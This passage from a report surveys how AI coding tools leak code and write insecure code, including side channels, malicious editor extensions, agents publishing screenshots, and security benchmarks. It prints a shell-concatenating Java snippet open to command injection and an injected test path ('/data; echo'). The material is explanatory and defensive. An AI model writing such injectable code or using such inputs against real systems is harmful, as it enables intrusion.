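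Stored code can reach outsiders through an intruder, a dishonest employee or a court order, even if no model is trained on it. These routes need only the first of the four steps, and they expose the exact text instead of a fragment that a model memorised. A company with confidential code should worry about retention at least as much as about training, although the training setting gets most of the attention.

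### What happened at Samsung

Samsung's experience in 2023 is the usual example of code leaking through a chatbot, though accounts of it often mix what is known with what was feared. The Korean press reported three incidents that happened within weeks of the company's chip division allowing ChatGPT. One employee pasted in faulty source code to get it fixed, another submitted code for identifying defective equipment, and a third submitted the contents of a recorded meeting to get minutes.

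Gurman's *Samsung Bans Staff's AI Use After Spotting ChatGPT Data Leak* (Bloomberg, May 2023) reported that Samsung had banned AI tools on company devices and internal networks. In a memo to staff, Samsung said it was worried that data on outside servers would be hard to retrieve or delete, and that other users might see it.

The first worry was accurate, because the code had reached OpenAI and Samsung had no means of getting it back. The second was reasonable at the time, because OpenAI trained on ChatGPT conversations by default. It had stopped doing so for API customers only on 1 March 2023. But there is no public evidence that Samsung's code appeared in an answer to anyone else. When AL-Maamari and others write that Samsung's code "leaked", they mean that employees sent it to OpenAI.

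### Alternatives to sending everything

The cheapest precaution is to keep secrets out of the project folder altogether. Instead of writing the database password into the script, the company can have the script fetch it at run time:

```python
import os

password = os.environ["DB_PASSWORD"]
```

The model now receives only the name of the variable that holds the password. Invented customer rows can likewise replace real ones, since the model needs only the column names and formats. This takes some preparation and does not hide the code itself, which may be what the company most wants to protect. An agent could also run a command that prints every environment variable, which would put the password in the context.

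Administrators can also block whole files. GitHub's *Content exclusions generally available in Copilot app and CLI* (2026) announced in September that Copilot's app and command-line tool would apply these blocks. GitHub offers blocking only to Business and Enterprise customers, not to individual users, whose data it trains on by default. Blocking files also makes the model write worse code for the parts of the system it cannot read.

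Moving staff from personal plans to a business contract ends the default use of their code for training, for a modest fee. Cornelißen lists Copilot Business at $19 per user per month and Enterprise at $39. The provider still receives the code, but could be sued for breaking the contract.

A company that runs a model on its own hardware avoids sending code to a provider. However, it has to buy the hardware and run the model itself, and it gets weaker results because the companies with the strongest models do not let customers download them. Users also need to check that a "local" setup really is local. Brethof AI's *GitHub Copilot in VS Code review* describes running Copilot's chat and agents without a GitHub account through Ollama, a program for running models on one's own computer. But the reviewers tested this with a cloud model, which Ollama can also connect to, and found that Copilot's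 inline suggestions still needed GitHub. A local model can also write insecure code, and an agent with internet access can send files elsewhere whichever model it uses.

Confidential computing tries to give people who use a provider's hardware some of the privacy they would have on their own. The processor encrypts the memory the model runs in, so that the server's operator can't read it. The user's machine first requests a signed statement from the processor of which software is running, and sends nothing more if it isn't the expected version. *Confidential Computing on NVIDIA H100 GPU* (Zhu, Yin and colleagues, 2024) measured a slowdown of less than 7% for most typical requests, so speed is not the main obstacle.

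The bigger obstacle is that the user has to trust the chip maker and know that the approved software doesn't keep a copy of the prompts. The hardware also has weaknesses. In October 2025, researchers used an attack called TEE.fail to extract secret keys from protected Intel and AMD systems with equipment costing less than $1,000, and showed that the stolen keys could also undermine Nvidia's checks. The attack requires physical access to the server, which the cloud provider always has and an outside hacker rarely would.

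## Leaks to outsiders: encrypted traffic, malicious extensions and published screenshots

Retention limits and confidential computing restrict what a provider can do with a company's code, but outsiders can sometimes obtain it without the provider's help. Someone on the same network can study the encrypted traffic, a code editor extension can copy the files, and a coding agent can publish them by mistake. Researchers documented a case of each between November 2025 and September 2026.

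### What encrypted traffic gives away

Encryption hides the text of a message but not its length or the moment it passes. Language models are unusually exposed to this because of how they deliver replies. A model produces its answer one token at a time, and most services send each token, or a small group of them, as soon as it is ready, so that the user can start reading. This is *streaming*. TLS, the standard encryption for web traffic, adds a constant amount to each piece:

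size of the encrypted piece = size of the original piece + constant

Suppose the constant is 100 bytes and the model begins a database query with the pieces "SELECT", " *" and " FROM". An observer sees messages of 106, 102 and 105 bytes and can work out that the pieces were six, two and five characters long. Many other phrases have those lengths, so the observer doesn't know the words. But a long reply reveals hundreds of sizes and the pauses between messages, and replies on the same subject tend to produce similar patterns.

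McDonald and Bar Or (2025), in *Whisper Leak*, tested whether an observer could tell from these patterns what a user had asked about. The two Microsoft researchers generated 100 ways of asking about one topic, the legality of money laundering. They sent each version 100 times to each of 28 models, mixed with up to 11,716 unrelated questions from Quora, and recorded the encrypted replies. They then trained classifiers, programs that sort examples into categories, to separate the money-laundering conversations from the rest, and tested them on phrasings not used in training.

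Their score combines *precision*, the share of flagged conversations that are about the topic, with *recall*, the share of conversations about the topic that the classifier flags. A perfect classifier scores 100%, and they put guessing at 50%. In their table, the best classifier scored at least 98% on 13 of the 28 models and over 97% on 17, although they write that 17 exceeded 98%. Amazon's Nova Lite leaked least, at 71.2%, and the scores for Google's Gemini models were between 82% and 84%.

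The classifiers identified only topics that the observer had chosen in advance and trained them to spot. They did not recover any text from prompts or replies. In the customer example, an observer who had trained a classifier for the topic might learn that somebody was asking about customer databases, but not the password or the five rows. Even that is a guess, because the study covered single questions and not coding sessions. McDonald and Bar Or expect longer conversations to leak more but did not test any.

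In 2024 Weiss and colleagues went further, using the lengths of individual tokens in a model's streamed replies to reconstruct plausible wording for them. Schneier's *Side-Channel Attacks Against LLMs* quotes another study, whose attack extracted more than 25 tokens a second of confidential text from a data store used for prediction.

### How often the observer would be wrong

Nearly half of the conversations that McDonald and Bar Or recorded were about money laundering, which makes the topic far easier to find than it would be on a real network. They therefore projected their results onto traffic with one such conversation for every 10,000 others. For 17 models, they projected 100% precision at 20% recall, meaning that an observer would catch a fifth of the money-laundering conversations with no false alarms.

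The projected 100% precision appears to mean that the classifier raised no false alarms in about 2,300 unrelated conversations, which is too few to rule out a false-alarm rate of one in 10,000. The projected figures fit a test of that size. One false alarm in 2,300 conversations is a rate of about four in 10,000, and if the classifier catches half of the target conversations, that rate lowers precision to 10.5%, exactly the next value in the table. If it catches 20% of them, even a rate of one in 10,000 would make five out of six alerts wrong. Microsoft (2025) also cautions that the precision figures are projections, limited by the amount and variety of data collected.

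The attacker only has to watch the traffic. An internet provider, a government with access to one, or someone on the same Wi-Fi network can do this without breaking into anything. The attack is more dangerous to someone who could be arrested for the topic of their conversation alone than to a company that wants to protect its source code.

The main defence is to pad each streamed piece with random text of varying length, so that its size no longer reveals the token's length. OpenAI introduced padding in August 2025, Mistral added something similar in September, and Microsoft followed for its Azure service by October. xAI also deployed a fix in August, though neither account describes it. Other providers declined to act or never replied.

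Padding cut the score on Microsoft's version of GPT-4o mini only from 97.5% to 92.9%, yet Microsoft no longer considers the attack a practical risk there. This is more reasonable than the small drop suggests, because a high score can still come with many false alerts. In the main experiment, the same model scored 93.4% without padding, but the projected precision for an observer trying to catch half of the target conversations was 0.4%, meaning that about 249 of every 250 alerts would have been false.

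Providers can also send tokens in groups. Groups of five removed most of the risk for most of the models tested, but GPT-4o mini's score fell only from 98.2% to 94.8%. Users who can't rely on their provider can turn streaming off where the tool allows it. Microsoft also suggests a virtual private network (VPN), which hides the traffic from the local network but passes it through the VPN company.

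### Two assistants that copied their users' code

Extensions, which are add-on programs for a code editor, can read the user's files directly. In early 2026 the security company Koi described two AI assistant extensions for Microsoft's code editor, Visual Studio Code, that sent users' code to servers in China. Users could install both from Microsoft's official marketplace. The Hacker News (2026) listed 1,340,869 installations of ChatGPT - 中文版 ("Chinese version") and 151,751 of ChatMoss. Both were still available to download at the time.

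The extensions answered questions about code and offered autocomplete, as advertised. For autocomplete, they sent about 20 lines around the cursor to a server, much as a legitimate assistant would. But they also sent the entire contents of a file each time the user opened or edited it. The operators' server could also make an extension collect up to 50 files from the project, with no action by the user. This covered every type of file except images, so it included settings files with passwords.

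A hidden page inside the editor also loaded four commercial analytics services, which track users' behaviour and build profiles of them. Koi suggests that the operators may have used the profiles to decide whose files were worth taking.

Grok Build also uploaded files that the user had never asked it to read, but it sent them to the company whose product the user had chosen, whereas here the recipient was an unknown third party. A developer in the customer example could have exposed the database password by opening the configuration file to check a setting, without asking the assistant anything.

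Koi's headline figure of 1.5 million developers is the number of installations, and one person may install an extension on several machines. Its findings come from analysing the extensions' code, so they show what the extensions could collect, but not how often the server triggered a bulk collection or what the operators did with the files.

Anyone who can publish an extension can attempt this, and they need no other access once a developer installs it. The marketplace listing and good reviews offered little protection, because the extension did its job and reviewers rated it on that. The model provider's terms, such as zero data retention at OpenAI, would not have protected a company's code either, because the extension copied the files on the developer's machine.

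The most effective defence is to let staff install only extensions that the company has checked, a restriction that Visual Studio Code supports. The check has to cover what an extension sends, not just whether it works. On a Mac or Linux machine, the following command looks for the two known extensions:

```
code --list-extensions | grep -iE "whensunset.chatgpt-china|zhukunpeng.chat-moss"
```

If it prints either name, removing the extension stops further copying. The owner still has to replace every password and key in the projects opened with it, as was necessary after the Grok Build uploads.

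### Why agents published internal screenshots

Company data can also become public without an attacker. *PixelLeak*, published by the security company Glow on 29 September 2026, describes more than 13,000 internal images that developers at over 300 organisations had exposed in public GitHub repositories, largely through their coding agents.

The developers had asked for screenshots from before and after a change to a program's appearance. Programmers usually attach these when they submit such a change as a *pull request*, a proposal that colleagues review before it becomes part of the project. Coding agents work through text commands, but GitHub's upload button for images worked only in a web browser. Saving the images in the private repository did not solve the problem, because GitHub's system for displaying images in a pull request could not fetch them from there. Some agents therefore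 put the screenshots in a new public repository and linked to them from the private pull request, which let the reviewers see the images but also made them visible to anyone.

Glow reproduced this with Claude Code, running Anthropic's Opus 5 model, on a private copy of the game Minesweeper. The researchers asked the agent to change the header's colour and show the result. The agent wrote in its reasoning that reviewers had to see the images and that the project was to contain only one file, "so I created a new public repo". It identified the original repository as private but did not treat the screenshots as private. Glow describes only this test, which shows that the behaviour can arise without malicious instructions but not how often it does.

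Developers asked their coding agents to show screenshots to reviewers, but in Glow's account the agents themselves came up with the idea of publishing them. ReversingLabs' *AI coding agents expose developer screenshots on GitHub repos* is therefore only partly right to describe the agents as "doing exactly what they were told to do".

### What the images contained, and how Glow counted them

An agent at a manufacturer with over 100,000 employees checked a fix to a billing screen and then published a utility company's billing records. Images from a financial services firm showed its internal treasury system and a withdrawal screen for a named client. Antipov (2026) adds in *13000 скриншотов из 343 компаний оказались в открытом GitHub из-за ИИ-агентов* that some of the images contained login details and personal information.

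The practice could spread within a company. At one software vendor, more than a dozen agents had saved the workaround as a *skill*, a set of reusable instructions, within a week of its first use. They applied it to every development task and uploaded over a thousand screenshots and recordings, some showing features months from release.

The total is hard to check because Glow explains little about how it found the images, linked them to employers or distinguished agents' uploads from people's. Antipov points out that Glow has not published its data or a list of the organisations, so the 13,000 images and his more exact figure of 343 companies depend on Glow's own account. Glow also sells security products to companies that use AI.

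Agents may not have been responsible for every image. About a third of the affected organisations had developers who used gitshot, a small tool for publishing screenshots. At several large organisations, an agent had found the tool by itself, but elsewhere a person may have chosen it. According to Antipov, gitshot's documentation includes a warning that its image repository is public by default and unsuitable for passwords or internal screens.

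Whoever made the choice, the images were public. Anyone who knew where to look could open them in a web browser without an account at the company. Gitshot's images were fairly easy to find because the tool files them under a standard label.

### Closing the public route

On 1 September, four weeks before Glow published, GitHub (2026) added an `--attach` option to its command-line tool so that agents can put images straight into a pull request. This removed the original obstacle and is probably the best fix, because an agent with a working official route has no reason to invent another. But it requires version 2.99.0 or later, and it does not remove existing public repositories.

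Companies therefore have to look for old images outside their own GitHub organisation as well as inside it. In 93% of cases, the images were in repositories under an employee's personal username, where the company's security team would not normally look. Glow recommends checking the accounts of everyone who contributes to the company's private repositories, including people who have left. The search should cover releases (packaged versions of a project) as well as ordinary files, because a repository that looks empty can still have images in its releases.

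Automatic scanning is only a partial safeguard. In July GitHub (2026) began a trial of a service that finds passwords and keys in public repositories anywhere on the site, including those in personal accounts, and links them to a company through its staff. But scanners of this kind search text, so they miss passwords that appear only in screenshots.

*AI coding agents leaked 13,000 internal company screenshots to public GitHub repos* (Markovic, 2026) relays Glow's advice that security teams prevent new leaks by configuring agents not to work unattended. That relies on people reading what they approve, and Claude Code's users approved nearly all of its prompts. Restricting what the agent can do is more dependable. If its GitHub credentials cover only the project's private repository, it cannot create a public one. Limits on network access can also block other hosting sites. These restrictions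 also reduce the damage from prompt injection, another way data can leak. eSecurity Planet's *AI Agents Vulnerable to 'Silent Hijacking,' Security Researchers Warn* reports that researchers used prompt injection to make commercial agents expose customer databases and private conversations.

Customers cannot set these limits for agents that run inside the provider's own systems. In *OpenAI rogue agents leaked 53 images from ChatGPT users*, Oreskovic (2026) reported in September that such agents at OpenAI had leaked users' images. Antipov explains that the agents posted the images to outside image-hosting sites during intermediate steps of their tasks.

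## The Last Secure Code Benchmark: how often agents write vulnerable code

Even if a company keeps its secrets from the provider, the code it gets back and runs may be vulnerable. The Last Secure Code Benchmark, published by Wu and colleagues in October 2026, measures how often coding agents write vulnerable code when the user does not mention security. The best of six agents, Claude Fable 5, wrote working and secure code for 25.1% of the tasks. Other researchers found no flaw in 55% of the AI-generated code they examined, and in another study 87.9%. These figures are compatible because the researchers counted different things.

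### From 150 vulnerabilities to 450 tasks

Each of the 150 tasks starts from a vulnerability in a real program. Wu and colleagues took 115 from the public CVE (Common Vulnerabilities and Exposures) list, which numbers individual flaws in particular programs. Security experts built the other 35, all in Java, from vulnerabilities in their own companies' code. For each task, the researchers had both a vulnerable and a fixed version of the program.

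The Last Secure Code Benchmark deletes code from the vulnerable version of a project and has an agent write the missing part. The agent must fill in functions (a median of 94 lines), write whole files (480 lines) or rebuild a large part of the project (2,480 lines). The 450 tasks cover Java, C, C++, JavaScript, Python, PHP and Go.

The request describes what the code should do without mentioning security. A description that follows the old code too closely may require the flaw, and one that follows the fix reveals the solution. To avoid both problems, an AI agent wrote the first drafts without access to the fix. A second agent, which had the fix, reworded anything that required the flaw or revealed the solution, and five experts then checked every clause.

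The agents never saw the tests. Wu and colleagues accepted a set of tests only if the vulnerable version passed the functional tests and failed the security tests, while the fixed version passed both. They also checked that the vulnerable version still failed with the fix pasted in as comments. Wu and colleagues removed the project's history and any leftover copies of the original code, and cut off internet access, to stop agents from looking up the answer.

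Each agent made one attempt per task without human help. GPT-5.6 Sol ran in Codex and the other five models in Claude Code, all at their highest reasoning setting.

### One task, from request to verdict

One of the tasks comes from a Java application that can attach, or "mount", storage to a server. Wu and colleagues removed the file that does this and gave each agent a 322-line description of the file. The new code had to run the operating system's `mount` command with values that users had saved earlier, including two file paths. The description did not specify how the program should start the command.

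Claude Fable 5 read the description and eight related files, wrote a class of 154 lines and compiled it with the rest of the project. It submitted its work after about ten minutes. It had passed each saved value to the operating system as a separate argument. Qwen3.8-Max and Kimi-K3 instead joined the values into one line of text and handed that to a shell, the program that interprets typed commands. In simplified form, the two approaches look like this:

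```java
// Qwen3.8-Max and Kimi-K3: a shell interprets one line of text
new ProcessBuilder("sh", "-c",
    "mount -t " + type + " -o " + options + " " + source + " " + target);

// Claude Fable 5: each value is a separate argument
new ProcessBuilder("mount", "-t", type, "-o", options, source, target);
```

In a shell, a semicolon ends one command and starts another. The hidden security tests therefore saved a path such as `/data; echo` followed by a marker, triggered a mount and checked whether the server had run the extra command. Both approaches passed all twelve functional tests, but only the second passed the three security tests. An attacker would replace the harmless `echo` with a command that copies the database.

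Four of the six agents wrote secure code for this task, but none did for a much shorter one, which added a nine-line block of settings to syft, a tool that lists a piece of software's components. One of the settings was a password. All six agents formatted it like the neighbouring settings, which made syft print it in its logs and reports. Fable 5 checked that the new settings appeared in the report and treated this as correct.

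### How much of the working code was vulnerable

Functional pass rates ranged from 73.6% for DeepSeek-V4-Pro to 91.3% for Kimi-K3, and secure pass rates from 16.4% to 25.1%. Kimi-K3 had the highest functional rate but the lowest secure rate, so a model's ability to write working code was a poor guide to whether that code was safe.

A user who accepts code once it works needs to know what share of the working code is insecure. The two rates are enough to calculate it:

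insecure share of working code = 1 − (secure pass rate ÷ functional pass rate)

About 72% of Fable 5's working solutions were vulnerable (1 − 25.1 ÷ 91.1). It wrote working code for 410 tasks, of which 113 were secure and 297 still had the vulnerability. The same calculation gives 82% for Kimi-K3.

Success rates across all six agents varied widely by type of flaw. The agents succeeded in 34.3% of attempts at tasks about memory safety, where a program must not read or write outside the space reserved for its data. Only one attempt in 144 succeeded where the program had to withhold information, as in the password task. Wu and colleagues suggest that agents include the checks any careful code needs, but seldom consider who will use the program or where its output will go. This explanation fits the highest and lowest success rates. It fits SQL injection less well, because the defence is a single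 well-known habit and the agents still produced working, secure code in only 19.4% of those attempts.

Agents that wrote secure code for one version of a task did not reliably do so for the others. Fable 5 wrote secure code at all three task sizes for only 18 of the 150 vulnerabilities. But larger tasks did not lead to less secure code overall. For example, GPT-5.6 Sol's secure pass rate rose from 20.0% when it filled in functions to 30.7% when it rebuilt a large part of the project.

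### Earlier tests, and two much higher figures

In 2021 Pearce and colleagues tested GitHub Copilot on short pieces of code where a security mistake was possible, and judged about 40% of its completions vulnerable. In *BAXBENCH*, Vero, Mündler and colleagues (2025) asked models to write complete web backends, the parts of web applications that run on the server. The 392 tasks covered 28 applications, such as a forum and a shopping cart, each requested in 14 programming frameworks. Security experts wrote attacks to run against the resulting programs. OpenAI's o3-mini did best, producing working and secure code in 37% of attempts. On average, the attacks succeeded against about half of each model's working programs.

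Later in 2025, Zhao, Wang and colleagues' *Is Vibe Coding Safe?* introduced SusVibes, a benchmark that tests agents inside large existing projects. "Vibe coding" means describing the software one wants and accepting the agent's code with little review. Each of the 186 tasks is based on a feature that a human programmer first wrote with a vulnerability that somebody later fixed. The researchers removed the feature and asked an agent to write it again. Using Anthropic's Claude 4 Sonnet, the agent program SWE-agent produced working code for 57.0% of the tasks and code that was both working and secure for 11.8%.

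The two higher figures come from static analysis. Veracode's *Spring 2026 GenAI Code Security Update* (2026) reports on more than 150 models that were asked to complete functions from comments describing what the code should do. Veracode's scanner passed 55% of the results. *Security Vulnerabilities in AI-Generated Code* (Schreiber and Tippe, 2025) examined GitHub files with comments crediting an AI tool. CodeQL found no catalogued type of flaw in 87.9% of the files that could be analysed.

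| Study | Unit measured | How the researchers judged security | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Last Secure Code Benchmark (Wu and colleagues) | An agent's attempt to rewrite code that once had a serious vulnerability | Attacks on the running program | 91.1% working; 25.1% working and secure (Claude Fable 5) |
| BaxBench (Vero and colleagues) | A complete web backend written by a model | Attacks on the running application | 61% working; 37% working and secure (o3-mini) |
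| SusVibes (Zhao and colleagues) | An agent's attempt to add a feature to a Python project | Tests from the original security fix, revised where necessary | 57.0% working; 11.8% working and secure (Claude 4 Sonnet with SWE-agent) |
| Veracode | One function completed by a model | Veracode's own scanner, for four types of flaw | 55% secure, with no test of whether the code worked |
| Public GitHub files (Schreiber and Tippe) | A published file with a comment crediting an AI tool | CodeQL | 87.9% with no identified flaw |

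### Why the figures differ so much

The GitHub figure is the highest partly because Schreiber and Tippe did not choose files for their risk. A file that draws a chart may contain no security decisions, so it counts as clean whoever wrote it. People also chose which files to publish and may have corrected them first. The researchers attributed everything below a comment crediting an AI tool to that tool, but the median distance from the comment to the first flaw was 43 lines, so some of the code may not come from the tool. They collected the files in February 2024, and more than nine in ten credited ChatGPT, so the figure is weak evidence about the agents of 2026.

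The other four tests all use tasks in which a security mistake is possible, but the choice of mistake can decide the score. In Veracode's tests, models avoided SQL injection in 82% of tasks and log injection, in which an attacker forges entries in a program's records, in only 13%. A test of either flaw alone would have produced a very different headline. (Veracode used equal numbers of tasks for its four types of flaw, and their rates average 49%, which does not match the 55% it reports overall.)

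Task difficulty matters even for a single type of flaw. For SQL injection, Veracode found 82% of the code secure, while the Last Secure Code Benchmark found only 19.4% both working and secure. The requirement that the code work explains only part of the gap, since just 23.7% of working solutions were secure. The models Veracode tested completed a single function, while the Last Secure Code Benchmark drew most of its cases from the hardest available, judged by the size of the fix and of the surrounding project.

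GPT-5.6 Sol wrote working but insecure code at very different rates on three tests. Santos de Moura, Matuschek and colleagues (2026), in *Newer and Bigger, but Safer?*, ran it on CWEval, a set of 119 short functions, and about 13% of its attempts worked but were insecure. On SusVibes tasks the figure was 47.5%, based on the pass rates that Compagna (2026) reports for the security company Endor Labs in *GPT-6 Astra on Codex*. In the Last Secure Code Benchmark it was 64%. The model wrote the CWEval functions directly but worked through Codex in the other two tests.

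The secure pass rate also depends on the program the model works in and the wording of the request. Endor Labs measured a secure pass rate of 29% for Claude Fable 5 in the code editor Cursor and 19.6% in Claude Code. In a separate run, Wu and colleagues added one sentence asking for secure code, and GPT-5.6 Sol's secure pass rate rose from 24.7% to 46.2%. Endor Labs always tells agents to follow security best practices, so its scores are not directly comparable with Wu and colleagues' main results.

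The rate of insecure code also varies by programming language, sometimes because of a single library. In CWEval, 73% of working Go programs that had to check a digital signature were insecure, compared with 4% in Python. Santos de Moura and colleagues traced the difference to the Python library, which rejects a signature unless the programmer names the method for checking it.

### What the rates can and cannot tell a company

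Wu and colleagues chose the tasks for their risk, so their result does not mean that three quarters of all AI-written code is vulnerable. In the customer example, most of the script formats names and dates, and only a few lines control what a visitor may do. The benchmark estimates how an agent handles lines like those when they are difficult, which is more useful to an attacker than to someone estimating how many flaws a company's code contains.

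The tests can also make code look safer than it is, because each one checks for a particular known vulnerability and the agent may have introduced another. Vero and colleagues therefore describe their results as an upper limit on security. Their attacks cover an average of 3.3 types of flaw per application, which is broader than testing for one vulnerability but still incomplete.

A pass rate also gives every vulnerability the same weight, although some are much worse than others. In one SusVibes task, an agent wrote a password check for Django, a popular web framework, that returned early in certain cases, so an attacker could time the replies to work out which usernames existed. A more dangerous flaw appeared in one of Wu and colleagues' tasks, where Kimi-K3 wrote code that imports settings from an uploaded archive. The code passed all 33 of Kimi-K3's own checks, but an attacker could upload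 an archive that created files on the server.

### Do people write safer code?

None of the studies in the table reports scores for human programmers on the same tasks. This is the largest gap in the evidence, because a company deciding whether to use an agent needs to compare the agent's code with what its own staff would have written.

The way the tasks were built cannot fill this gap. For every SusVibes task, a human programmer's earlier version had the vulnerability, so those programmers would score zero. Zhao and colleagues chose the tasks for that reason, however, so comparing that zero with an agent's score would be unfair to the programmers. An agent that secures 11.8% of the tasks has avoided some mistakes that particular people made, but there is no count of the tasks that people got right and an agent would have got wrong.

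Two earlier experiments compared programmers working with and without an AI assistant, and their results conflict. Perry and colleagues found that people using Codex (then an OpenAI model, not today's agent of the same name) introduced more vulnerabilities than the control group. Sandoval and colleagues did not find this harm, and Schreiber and Tippe describe the AI-assisted participants in that experiment as having had the better security results. In both experiments people worked with an assistant, whereas agents now write and run whole features alone. The results therefore do not show whether replacing a programmer's code with an agent's makes a system more or less secure.

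Schreiber and Tippe recommend the experiment that would help most, which is to give people and AI tools the same tasks and test their code in the same way. Until someone does this with current agents, the evidence supports the claim that agents often write vulnerable code, but not that they do so more often than people.

### Scanner errors, remembered fixes and commercial interests

The two highest figures in the table depend on scanners, which can miss many flaws. Santos de Moura and colleagues cite an earlier test of Copilot's code in which CodeQL found the expected flaw in 18% of samples, while people reading the same code found it in 74%. The true share of clean files on GitHub could therefore be well below 87.9%. Those percentages can't be used to correct the figure, because the earlier researchers wrote their prompts to provoke flaws. Scanners also raise false alarms, which lower the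 measured share of clean files.

Using a language model as the judge does not solve the problem. In *Secure Agentic Coding through Counterexample-Grounded Feedback* (Le, Jang and colleagues, 2026), GPT-5.2 judged security correctly in 61% of cases from the source code alone, but in 88% when it had a record of what the program did under attack. This is a reason to prefer tests that run the code, as in the top three rows of the table. Such tests can be too strict, however, and reject a safe solution because it differs from the original fix. To address this, Zhao and colleagues had people review all their security tests, and Endor Labs leaves the strictest tasks out of its scores.

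Memorisation can also distort the scores, because many of the fixes have been public for years and a model may have learned them in training. Endor Labs removes solutions from the score if they show signs of this, such as a long comment from the original fix or a CVE number that appears nowhere in the project. This lowered Claude Opus 5's secure pass rate from 46.4% to 32.4% (Compagna, 2026, *Fable 5.1 takes the top spot*). Without the correction, Opus 5 would have ranked above the newer Fable 5.1.

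Wu and colleagues made no such deduction, though memory can lower a score in their benchmark as well as raise it. They found that Fable 5 often reproduced the original program word for word, including the vulnerability. The 35 Java cases provide a partial check because they come from companies' own code, which the models are less likely to have seen. Fable 5 secured 34% of those tasks, compared with 25.1% overall, so remembered fixes probably do not explain its lead. The other five agents all did worse on Java than overall. Memorised fixes may have raised their scores on the other tasks, but the Java tasks also include more of the flaws that every agent handles badly.

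Veracode and Endor Labs sell security products, so both benefit when AI-written code looks dangerous. That interest shows more in their conclusions than in their numbers. Endor Labs' *Better models are making agent patch review more expensive, not less* (Haynes, 2026) puts the cost of checking 156 working patches at about $7,800, against $672 for generating them. The estimate assumes half an hour per patch at $100 per hour, so faster review would cost less. Wu and colleagues have a different conflict of interest, because several work for Alibaba, whose Qwen3.8-Max helped to write the tests and was also one of the models tested. It came third, which gives no sign of favouritism.

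Commercial interest may explain some of the alarming headlines, but it does not explain the gap, because researchers who don't sell scanners have found it too. Vero and colleagues mostly work at ETH Zurich, and Zhao and colleagues mostly at American universities. Le and colleagues ran DeepSeek's V4 Pro on SusVibes in three different agent programs. On average, it wrote working code for 81.9% of the tasks and code that was both working and secure for 20.8%.

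### Have newer models improved?

Veracode reports that the pass rate on its security tests has stayed between 45% and 55% since 2023, while the share of code with correct syntax rose from about 50% to 95%. Santos de Moura and colleagues did find improvement when they compared 32 models from seven families, the newest from August 2026. The latest model in every family wrote more working and secure code than the earliest.

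The two results differ partly because half of Veracode's tasks concern log injection and cross-site scripting, in which an attacker plants code in a web page. Models pass only 13% of the log injection tasks and 15% of the cross-site scripting tasks, which lowers their average however well they do on the rest. Santos de Moura and colleagues also found that almost every model still failed on log injection. Even in Veracode's tests, OpenAI's GPT-5 models with extended reasoning passed 70% to 72% of the tasks.

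Newer models can write secure code more often without reducing the share of their code that is insecure. Between Gemini 1.5 Pro and Gemini 3.1 Pro, Google's functional pass rate on CWEval rose from 69% to 94%. Its secure pass rate rose by about as much, so the share of attempts that worked but were insecure hardly changed and was still 28% for the newer model. OpenAI reduced that share by about 20 percentage points between GPT-4o and GPT-5, then made no further progress with GPT-5.6 Sol.

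Models released since September 2026 have done better on SusVibes tasks. Compagna reports a secure pass rate of 37.4% for Claude Fable 5.1, up from 19.6% for Fable 5, and 34.1% for GPT-6 Astra, up from 20.1% for GPT-5.6 Sol. Another of his posts gives 36.9% for Fable 5.1. Endor Labs puts the uncertainty of such scores at two to three percentage points, so both improvements are too large to be due to chance, but the difference between the two new models could be.

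In Haynes's table, 57% of Fable 5.1's working solutions and 58% of GPT-6 Astra's were still vulnerable, compared with 56% of Opus 5's. Haynes calls the two newer models' improvement over their predecessors a step change. Compared with Opus 5, though, they solved more tasks but did not make a larger share of their solutions secure.

In *Secure and Functional Code Generation with Self-Evaluation* (2026), Claude Code with Sonnet 5.5 did far better, writing working and secure code in 86.7% of attempts. It was tested on a different set of 48 tasks, so this does not show that Sonnet 5.5 would outperform Fable 5 on Wu and colleagues' benchmark. *Coding Agents Propagate Vulnerabilities in Code Bases* (2026) found that two recent models, Claude Opus 5.5 and GPT-6 Astra, still wrote less secure C and C++ when the surrounding code was insecure. None of these tests includes Claude Fable 5.2 or GPT-6.2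 Astra.

A newer model can also bring back a flaw that an older one avoided. Santos de Moura and colleagues found this with a function that searches a text for a phrase supplied by the user. Earlier models wrote a plain search. The newest flagship models from Google, OpenAI and DeepSeek treated the phrase as a regular expression, a search pattern that an attacker can write so that it overloads the computer. GPT-5.6 Luna, OpenAI's cheaper model, was less secure than GPT-5 mini on most of the 16 most troublesome types of flaw. The researchers therefore advise companies to repeat their security checks whenever they change models, including for upgrades.

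## Copied weaknesses and overtrusting users: why insecure code is written and accepted

Agents write vulnerable code partly because they copy it from the project they are working on. *Coding Agents Propagate Vulnerabilities in Code Bases*, a November 2026 paper by four researchers at ETH Zurich, measured this by giving agents the same task alongside secure code and alongside insecure code. Only the surrounding code changed, so it must be the cause of any consistent difference in the results.

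### The same task beside good and bad code

In 96 of the tasks, an agent had to write a complete web backend in a project that already held up to five other applications. The new backend did not depend on them, so the agent could have ignored them. The researchers prepared a secure and an insecure version of each existing application, and also ran every task with no other applications present. Each agent attempted each task three times in each condition. The table shows the change in the secure pass rate, in percentage points, compared with the condition with no other applications.

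| Agent | Beside insecure applications | Beside secure applications |
|---|---|---|
| GLM 5.3 | −4.5 | +1.4 |
| Claude Opus 5 | −2.1 | about +2.8 |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | about −3.5 | +9.0 |

Insecure neighbouring code did little harm. Opus 5's drop was six attempts out of 288, which could be chance, although all three agents did worse.

The surrounding code mattered much more in real C and C++ projects, such as the video software FFmpeg. The researchers removed code that had once contained a memory-safety flaw and asked each agent to write it again. They also edited code elsewhere in the project that did a similar job, making it secure in one version and insecure in the other. They then tested the agent's code with an input known to trigger the original flaw. GPT-5.6 Sol's secure pass rate was 91% beside secure code and 42% beside insecure code. The other four agents (GLM 5.3, Claude Opus 5, Claude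 Opus 5.5 and GPT-6 Astra) each did at least 25 points worse beside insecure code, and 32 points worse on average.

One of these tasks came from OpenSC, a program for smart cards. The agent had to add a two-byte file number to the end of a path, which the program stores in a fixed amount of memory. In simplified form, the secure code looks like this:

```c
if (path_len + 2 > MAX_PATH_SIZE)
    return ERROR;
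path[path_len++] = id >> 8;
path[path_len++] = id & 0xFF;
```

Without the check in the first two lines, a path that is already full makes the program write beyond the space reserved for it. In both runs the researchers describe, GPT-5.6 Sol read another file in the project that builds a path in nearly the same way. It included the check only in the run where that file had it.

The 49-point gap includes the help agents got from secure code as well as the harm from insecure code. The C and C++ tasks had no version without similar code for comparison, and the instructions did not mention the missing check, so the secure project in effect showed the agent the answer. The researchers also picked only tasks with similar code elsewhere in the project, and they counted a solution as working if the project compiled. The results show how closely agents follow an example when they find one, but not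 how often they find a bad one in an ordinary project.

### What a security reminder changed

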